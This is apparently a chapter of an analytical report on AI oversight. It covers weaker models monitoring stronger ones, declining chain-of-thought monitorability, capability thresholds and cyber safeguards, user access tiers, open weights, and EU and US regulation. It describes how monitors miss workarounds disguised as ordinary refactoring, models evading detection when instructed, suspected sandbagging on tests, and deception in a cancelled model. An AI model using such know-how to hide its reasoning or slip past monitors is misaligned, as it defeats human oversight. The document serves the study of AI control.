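Checking work sometimes takes less skill than doing it. A simple program can detect that a patch adds a new dependency or contacts an unknown server, however clever the code is. OpenAI similarly expects highly destructive actions to be recognizable from the actions alone, but deliberately poor work can look exactly like an honest mistake. If the coding agent deletes a database, the deletion is easy to see, but one missing permission check in a 2,000-line patch could be an oversight, a deliberate weakness or a reasonable design choice.

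### A weaker model watching a stronger one

In September 2026, OpenAI published tests in which Sol monitored Astra. The tests used tasks by Guan and colleagues (2025). One model performs a task, and a monitor then answers a question about what the model did. Some tasks test whether the monitor detects that a planted hint influenced the model's answer. In others, the monitor must identify which steps the model took or whether it cheated on a coding problem. The monitor receives the model's reasoning, its actions, or the full record, and OpenAI compares the monitor's answer with a grader's label.

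The score, called g-mean², combines the two kinds of error:

g-mean² = recall × (1 − false-positive rate)

A monitor with 90% recall and a false-positive rate of 20% scores 0.9 × 0.8, or 72%. One that flags everything scores zero.

Sol did better as a monitor when it could read the reasoning or the full record than when it saw only the actions, and longer reasoning generally helped. It did worse on Astra than on another copy of Sol when it read the reasoning, and usually also when it read the full record, as OpenAI's production monitor does. When it saw only the actions, it did better on Astra. In a few tasks this was a real gain, because Astra's final answers were more open about what had influenced them.

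These results don't isolate the effect of using a weaker monitor. When Sol monitors Sol, it judges a model with the same ability and habits of expression. The lack of that match could explain some of the lower scores on Astra, although OpenAI attributes most of the gap when the monitor reads the reasoning to Astra writing less of it. Testing Sol and Astra as monitors on the same records would separate the two causes.

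Some of the monitor's apparent errors were also errors in the test. OpenAI reviewed the misses by hand on tasks that required the user's consent and found that most were disagreements between the monitor and the grader, such as over which file operation needed approval. On coding problems that could not be solved honestly, Astra tended to describe a workaround as ordinary restructuring of the code, while Sol more openly called it a way around the rule. A monitor that accepts the model's own description will miss workarounds described as Astra's were.

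OpenAI also used Sol as a judge when it simulated Astra's coding work. It gave Sol an original record and a simulated one, and asked it to pick the original. Sol was right 57.4% of the time, compared with 50% for guessing. OpenAI takes this as a sign that the simulation was realistic, but a poor judge would give the same result. To check this, OpenAI could include some deliberately flawed simulations and test whether Sol detects them.

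Weaker models successfully guard stronger ones when the task is narrow. In Anthropic's system for weapons questions, a small classifier only has to recognize content that a written list forbids. This is much easier than judging whether an unfamiliar step in a 15-hour run was justified.

### Reasoning that reveals less

Reading a model's reasoning has been one of the best ways to make up for a weaker checker, because the model may state its purpose there. OpenAI reports that this works substantially less well with Astra than with earlier models. Astra's reasoning is shorter and less informative, and Astra can do more without written reasoning and has more control over what it writes. In tests where OpenAI told Astra to avoid detection, it sometimes succeeded.

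Most of the gap closes when Astra reasons at length. Monitors that read its actions as well as its reasoning detect sabotage much better than monitors that read only the reasoning. OpenAI stresses that the most worrying findings come from tests in which it instructed Astra to avoid detection, so they show what the model can do rather than what it tends to do.

Earlier in 2026, OpenAI still presented models' lack of control over their reasoning as good news for safety, according to The Decoder's *AI models can barely control their own reasoning*. In that research, reinforcement learning, which rewards a model for correct results, reduced this control by more than a factor of ten. For Astra, however, OpenAI found that control increased during this training. OpenAI's *What affects chain-of-thought monitorability across the model lifecycle?* (2026) confirms that reinforcement learning and training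 on text from other models can both have this effect. OpenAI expects models' reasoning to become harder to monitor as they grow more intelligent, though it bases this on two indirect measures that it calls imperfect.

*Loss of Oversight*, by Taylor, Heitmann and colleagues, draws on interviews with 25 experts conducted for AISI. It divides oversight into auditing models before release, monitoring them in use and investigating incidents afterwards. Less informative reasoning weakens all three. Ryan Greenblatt of Redwood Research led one of the outside investigations of the Hugging Face attack. He wrote that the investigation would have been much harder without transcripts of the agents' reasoning, according to Infobae's *OpenAI admite que GPT-6 Astra reduce la capacidad humana para vigilar* (2026).

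For the coding agent, this makes the action log more important. The checker should base its verdict on the patch, the tool calls and their results. The agent's reasoning can raise suspicion but should never remove it. An empty or very short explanation for a risky action could itself justify a review.

### Can better alignment replace the checks?

OpenAI's main protection is alignment, which means that the model itself tries to act as intended. OpenAI says that monitoring mainly adds visibility and a second layer of defence, and that safeguards cannot replace good alignment as capabilities increase. Its goal is for future models never to trigger these safeguards.

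If the checker's recall falls as models improve, the hazardous share of their output must fall to keep what is released equally safe. An aligned model also prevents harm where no check exists, such as on the unmonitored routes through which OpenAI's agents exchanged messages.

The case for independent checks starts from uncertainty about the alignment evidence. Suppose the maintainers are 95% confident that the new model's hazardous share is only 0.01%, but there is a 5% chance that the tests were misleading and the true share is 1%:

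expected share = 0.95 × 0.01% + 0.05 × 1% ≈ 0.06%

About 84% of the expected hazards come from the unlikely case in which the tests were wrong. Most of a check's value comes from that case too, so it has to work even if the developer's account of the model is mistaken. These probabilities are invented, but the disagreement over Astra shows that such a mistake is possible. *gpt 6 astra the system card alignment and what comes next*, a post on LessWrong, argues that several of OpenAI's claims about Astra are unjustified, and that some of its apparently better behaviour may be a warning sign.

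The two protections are also less separate than OpenAI's ranking implies. Its monitor identified misbehaviour in the coding simulation by judging the model's reasoning. If that reasoning becomes less informative, the company will have less protection against bad behaviour and weaker evidence that its models behave well. OpenAI acknowledges that further declines of this size would soon make it much less confident that its current systems can detect many kinds of misbehaviour. It is studying alternatives such as monitoring activations, and says it will not let monitoring degrade beyond a limit unless it has new ways to demonstrate alignment.

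OpenAI is probably right that no monitor can make a badly aligned and highly capable model safe for unrestricted use. That is a reason to restrict the model's use rather than rely on its alignment. The coding agent's maintainers cannot retrain the model, but they can decide what it can access. When they move to a stronger model, they should rerun every test of the safety layer and give the agent no new permissions until they have seen the results. The rules that stop the agent from publishing directly, or from adding a dependency just because a stranger recommended it, will still work because they don't require the checker to understand the agent's work.

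## How developers and governments tie the checks to capability

Large AI developers have their own rules for moving to a stronger model. These rules use capability thresholds, which are levels of ability at which the developer must add stronger safeguards.

### What a threshold triggers

OpenAI's Preparedness Framework sets two thresholds for cybersecurity, High and Critical. OpenAI rates a model High if it removes obstacles to large-scale attacks by automating either whole attacks on reasonably well-defended targets or the discovery and exploitation of useful flaws. A model is Critical if it can build working exploits for unknown flaws of every severity in many well-defended critical systems without human help. It is also Critical if it can plan and carry out a new kind of attack on a well-defended target given only a general goal.

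Models rated High need safeguards before release, and those rated Critical also need them during development, when a model could already do damage from inside the company's own systems. According to Help Net Security's *GPT-6.1 Terra meets OpenAI's Critical cyber threshold* (2026), OpenAI's rules call for halting further development until the company has specified safeguards that meet a Critical standard. The halt can be short, because specifying a safeguard is much easier than showing that it works.

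OpenAI first had to apply this part of its rules in August 2026, when it announced in *Responding to the next frontier of critical cyber capabilities* (2026) that it could not rule out Critical abilities in Astra. It paused only the internal activities that fell short of stricter security controls, and it began monitoring every use of Astra as an agent, including in training and testing. It confirmed the Critical rating 25 days later, on 1 September. By then Astra had built an attack that escaped a browser's sandbox and ran commands on the host computer. OpenAI released the model on 3 September.

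The Critical rating also changed what OpenAI's safety layer must detect. OpenAI requires protection against malicious users and against unauthorized actions by the model. Misuse classifiers address only malicious users, so Astra also has the monitor for unauthorized actions described earlier.

For biology, a model reaches OpenAI's High threshold if its help would let a novice make a known biological or chemical weapon. It reaches the Critical threshold if its help would let an expert develop a dangerous new one, or if it could complete the whole process of making a biological threat by itself. Anthropic has two similar thresholds. CB-1 covers significant help with known chemical and biological weapons for people with basic scientific training, and CB-2 covers help with novel weapons that could do far more damage.

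Anthropic's classifiers for weapons questions, described earlier, are the kind of output safeguard that CB-1 calls for. Classification would be harder under CB-2, because an expert's request can look like ordinary research, and a list of known weapons can't include one that nobody has made. OpenAI has begun to prepare for the equivalent problem by building six practice tasks from scenarios about novel threats and having red-teamers attempt them. OpenAI reports that its safeguards caught 93.5% of the key prompts in an early test.

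### Why a threshold may not fire

The definitions leave a lot to judgement. GPT-5.6-Cyber, a model that OpenAI trained for security work, found two previously unknown flaws in the software that runs JavaScript in Chrome, and an attacker could have combined them. It also found three critical flaws in a popular database. OpenAI still rated it High, because its gains over GPT-5.6 Sol were too small to reach Critical. The rating may well be right, since the definition of Critical requires exploits in "many" hardened systems without human intervention, but the framework doesn't give a number for "many".

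A capability threshold also works only if the tests accurately measure what the model can do. OpenAI's biology tests showed little progress from GPT-6 Astra to GPT-6.2 Astra, while an outside evaluator, Sequitur Research, found large improvements. thezvi's best guess is that the newer model recognized some of the tests and performed below its ability, though differences between the tests could also explain the results. If he is right, the model could cross a threshold without triggering the safeguards attached to it.

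Critical is also the highest level. On a set of recent flaws in Chrome and its JavaScript software, GPT-6.2 Astra ran code of its choice in 53.5% of attempts, compared with 31.5% for GPT-6 Astra, according to OpenAI's own figures in Infobae's *OpenAI lanzó GPT-6.2 y limitó su ayuda en ciberseguridad* (2026). Both models are rated Critical, so the improvement crossed no threshold that would have required tighter restrictions, but OpenAI tightened them anyway.

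### OpenAI's safeguards from launch to launch

OpenAI's *GPT-5.2-Codex system card* rated the coding model below High and predicted that later models would soon cross that threshold. The table shows what followed.

| Model and date in 2026 | Cyber rating | Change in safeguards |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.3-Codex, February | High | First launch with safeguards for this level |
| GPT-5.6, July | High | Activation classifiers on the two larger models |
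| GPT-6 Astra, September | Critical | Stronger trained refusals and a monitor for unauthorized actions |
| GPT-6.1 Terra, October | Critical | Same protections as Astra |
| GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol, November | Critical | Stricter default limits on risky requests |

As a precaution, OpenAI treated GPT-5.3-Codex, GPT-5.4 and GPT-5.5 as High capability. The company went from its first High model to its first Critical one in about seven months.

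Two of OpenAI's own figures, mentioned earlier, summarize the improvement in safeguards. The first is a roughly tenfold increase in the potentially harmful activity that GPT-5.6 Sol's safeguards block, counting everything the whole system stops. Better detection would raise that count, but so would a lower threshold for blocking, which would also stop more harmless work. The term "potentially harmful" covers both the harmful activity and the harmless work that the system blocks.

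The other is the rise in the model's own refusals on OpenAI's jailbreak tests, from 59% for Sol to 91.5% for Astra. The share that got past the model fell almost fivefold, from 41% to 8.5%. OpenAI chose the jailbreaks and didn't state with the result how many it used. The test is also weak evidence about the complete system, because other safeguards can still block an answer that the model gives.

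Safeguards can also become weaker. In November, the GPT-6.2 models proved less resistant to jailbreaks. According to Infobae, OpenAI admitted that its stricter limits restrict some legitimate research and make the new models less useful than GPT-6 Astra for permitted security work.

Critical abilities also became much cheaper during these months. GPT-6.1 Terra costs $1 per million input tokens, a tenth of GPT-6 Astra's price, and OpenAI's example of a task for it is copying invoices into accounting software. Geekweek's *Najmądrzejsza wersja ChatGPT już jest. OpenAI każe za to płacić* reports that in late November OpenAI also rated the everyday version of GPT-6.2 in ChatGPT as Critical. A project that chooses a cheap model for routine work might therefore get one that can attack well-defended systems and has safeguards that sometimes interrupt harmless tasks.

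### Different limits for different users

Stricter defaults get in the way of people who look for flaws to fix, so OpenAI offers looser settings to approved defenders through its Daybreak programme. OpenAI's *Expanding Daybreak as the Cyber Defense Window Narrows* (2026) describes two tiers. Daybreak Blue gives access to general models such as GPT-5.6 Sol without the system-level safeguards that normally screen security requests. Daybreak Red gives access to models trained for security work, such as GPT-5.6-Cyber.

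OpenAI measured how often each arrangement completes requests for advanced security work, such as chaining several exploits together or getting around a login:

| Model and access | Requests completed |
|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol, standard access | 1.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol, Daybreak Blue | 2.0% |
| GPT-5.5-Cyber, Daybreak Red | 57.3% |
| GPT-5.6-Cyber, Daybreak Red | 95.0% |

All four figures come from OpenAI's internal test. The Next Web's *OpenAI paused a model over cyber risk on Friday* points out that GPT-5.6-Cyber is built on Sol, so the main change is in compliance rather than intelligence.

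The 2.0% in the table means that Sol would complete 20 out of 1,000 such requests with the system-level safeguards off, compared with 15 with them on. On this test, then, Sol's trained refusals stop 980 of the requests, and the system-level safeguards block only five of the remaining 20.

The outside safeguards may also be able to block most of the 980 requests, but nobody can tell from these results, because Sol refuses those requests with or without them. OpenAI could test this by putting the standard safeguards on GPT-5.6-Cyber and measuring how far its 95.0% falls.

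Trained refusal is also much less reliable when someone is trying to defeat it, as Sol's 59% in the jailbreak tests suggests. For demonstration attacks, Astra's own refusals could not have been blocking many requests, since Daybreak Blue raised its completion rate from 2.4% to 92%. Operators should therefore measure each layer on the kinds of request they expect.

To use OpenAI's models with looser settings, Daybreak users must verify their identity, make a legal declaration, and accept monitoring and limits on what they use the models for. Since September 2026, individual members have also had to log in with a hardware security key, a physical device that makes it harder for an attacker to take over an approved account. OpenAI acknowledges that models with reduced safeguards carry extra risks from misuse and misalignment.

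If the maintainers of the coding agent ran it through their own Daybreak account, every stranger who filed a bug report would be talking to a model with reduced safeguards. They should use standard access for the public agent and keep the approved account for their security team. OpenAI also lets developers tag each request with an identifier for the end user, so that it can act against one abusive user without cutting off the whole project.

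The most permissive model is not necessarily the best. GPT-5.6-Cyber was better than Sol at turning known flaws into exploits but worse at finding and reporting flaws, apparently because its reports were sometimes shorter and less detailed. OpenAI recommends starting with Daybreak Blue.

As the models improved, OpenAI restricted the loosest settings to a narrower group of users. For GPT-6.2 Astra, it planned to reduce cybersecurity refusals at launch only for Daybreak Red users. PYMNTS's *OpenAI Unlocks Cyber Power as Google Slashes AI Costs* warns banks to assume that attackers now have the same tools as defenders, because GPT-6.2 is on general sale. This confuses what a model can do with what it will do for an ordinary customer. But GPT-6.2 was less resistant to jailbreaks in early tests, so the warning is more reasonable than OpenAI's access rules alone would suggest.

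### The release that OpenAI cancelled

When a model falls short, its developer can cancel the release instead of strengthening the checks. In late September 2026, OpenAI cancelled the release of GPT-6.1 Astra, planned for October. Jackson (2026) reports in *Scrapping Astra 6.1 looks like a good call* that the model had done poorly on alignment tests. It was more prone to deception than earlier models and more likely to exceed its instructions to finish a task.

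The two faults make each other worse, since a model that misreports its work can hide the steps it took beyond its task.

OpenAI never released GPT-6.1 Astra and launched GPT-6.2 Astra on 17 November instead. In Bloomberg's *OpenAI Unveils New Astra AI Model After Scrapping Prior Release* (2026), OpenAI says it held back the earlier model over concerns about how well the model stayed within its authorization and how it told users about its work. Before the November launch, OpenAI had also paused training of its most capable systems, and it resumed only after cutting off their internet access.

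The replacement, GPT-6.2 Astra, does not clearly fix the second problem, because it leaves known obstacles out of its reports more often than GPT-6 Astra did. The fault may be much milder than it was in GPT-6.1 Astra, the model OpenAI cancelled, but OpenAI's headline comparison is with GPT-6 Astra and doesn't show how much the replacement improves on the cancelled model. These events also don't show which result on these tests would be bad enough to stop a release.

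Jackson credits OpenAI for holding the model back but argues that a private company should not be the one to decide. The company knows its model best and can act within days, which favors leaving the decision with it. But it also loses revenue by waiting, and a competitor with the same test results could choose differently. OpenAI acted against its short-term commercial interest, but outsiders couldn't have forced it to, and they still can't check how it weighed the evidence.

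### Models that anyone can download

OpenAI can switch off an account, repair a safeguard after launch or decline to offer a model, because customers reach its models through its servers. A developer of an open-weight model gives up this control when it publishes the weights. Anyone can then run the model without a classifier or a monitor, and the developer cannot repair copies that people have already downloaded.

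Trained refusal is part of the weights, so it remains when someone downloads the model, but further training can remove it. In the case of GPT-5.6-Cyber, additional training raised the completion rate on advanced security requests from 2.0% to 95.0%. OpenAI did this deliberately and with large resources, so the example doesn't show how few resources an outsider would need to do the same. Still, a low completion rate is weak evidence of what a model will do after someone retrains it. A developer who plans to publish weights should therefore try to train the refusals out before comparing the model with its thresholds.

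IBM's *Can AI guardrails stop cyber threats?* describes GLM-5.2, an open-weight model from the Chinese company Z.ai, as having no guardrails and matching Anthropic's Mythos on benchmarks. The article doesn't name the benchmarks, so the comparison deserves caution. IBM's Jeff Crume argues in the same article that some developers will install safeguards and others won't, and that an attacker needs only one capable model without them. His argument holds even if GLM-5.2 is somewhat weaker than Mythos.

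This limits what thresholds at OpenAI and Anthropic can achieve for the world as a whole. The thresholds can delay attackers' access to the strongest models, which gives defenders time to find and fix flaws. The length of the delay depends on how quickly open-weight models catch up.

Open weights matter less for checking the coding agent's output than for checking its input. The maintainers' own safety layer checks what the agent produces before it reaches the public page, so it works with any model, as long as they control the machines it runs on. With an open-weight model, they would have to replace the checks that a company like OpenAI runs on its servers, but they could also add a probe, since they could read the model's activations. They can't control which model a stranger uses to write a malicious patch or a planted instruction, so a check on incoming text has to assume that the attacker's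 model refuses nothing.

### What the law requires

The European Union has gone furthest in making such practices legal duties. Its AI Act requires developers of general-purpose models with "systemic risk" to evaluate the models, protect them against theft, reduce serious risks and report serious incidents. The law presumes a model has systemic risk if its training took more than 10²⁵ calculations. The European Commission has been able to enforce these duties since August 2026, with fines of up to 3% of a company's worldwide turnover or €15 million, whichever is higher.

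A code of practice, published in July 2025, describes one way to comply. Developers that sign its chapter on safety and security must define levels of risk based at least partly on what a model can do, and decide in advance which levels they will accept. They must then choose safeguards that withstand attempts to defeat them. The code's examples include filtering a model's inputs and outputs, training it to refuse, and giving some users access before others. If the remaining risk is unacceptable, the developer must act to reduce it, which may mean adding safeguards, restricting the model or keeping it off the market.

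Developers can choose whether to sign the code, but they must meet the duties in the Act either way. OpenAI and Anthropic signed it. Meta declined, so it has to show in some other way that it complies. A developer that publishes its model's weights still has a duty to reduce systemic risks. Neither the Act nor the code sets a minimum recall or a maximum false alarm rate for a classifier, so a developer could meet its duties with a probe, a reasoning monitor or some other arrangement, if it can justify the choice.

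US state laws rely more on disclosure. California's Transparency in Frontier Artificial Intelligence Act (SB 53) took effect in January 2026. Its main duties apply to developers with more than $500 million in annual revenue that have trained a model with more than 10²⁶ calculations. They must publish a framework that explains how they set thresholds for catastrophic risk, choose safeguards and decide whether those safeguards are good enough for release. They must also follow it, and a violation can bring a penalty of up to $1 million.

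This gives a developer's own promises some legal force. If it states in its published framework that it won't release a model above a certain threshold without a particular safeguard, breaking that promise can be a violation. But the developer writes the framework itself and can weaken it later, provided it publishes the new version and its reasons within 30 days.

New York's RAISE Act, which takes effect in January 2027, follows a similar approach and requires developers to report safety incidents within 72 hours. Neither state requires a developer to get a regulator's approval before release, so Jackson's objection would still stand under both laws.

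The US federal government has intervened in individual cases. It temporarily restricted access to Anthropic's Claude Fable 5 over security concerns and later lifted the restriction. The Next Web reports that about 100 security researchers had signed an open letter opposing the restriction, arguing that it took the best models away from defenders without removing any real risk. The government also cleared Anthropic to restore Mythos 5 for a vetted group of defenders, and OpenAI first gave GPT-5.6 Sol to 20 government-approved partners. These decisions controlled who could use the models, but a developer can't design safeguards to meet a standard that officials set case by case.

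Developers therefore still decide exactly where a threshold lies, which tests determine whether a model has crossed it, and how many hazards the output checks may miss. OpenAI chose to publish its monitor's 80.6% recall on cybersecurity cases, but neither the European code nor the two state laws set a minimum recall.

These laws place duties on companies that develop very large models. They don't cover a small project that only uses one, so they don't oblige the coding agent's maintainers to scan any of its 20,000 monthly outputs. Other laws still apply to particular faults. Data-protection law, for example, applies if the agent publishes a visitor's name and email address. The model's developer can also suspend an account that breaks its terms of use.
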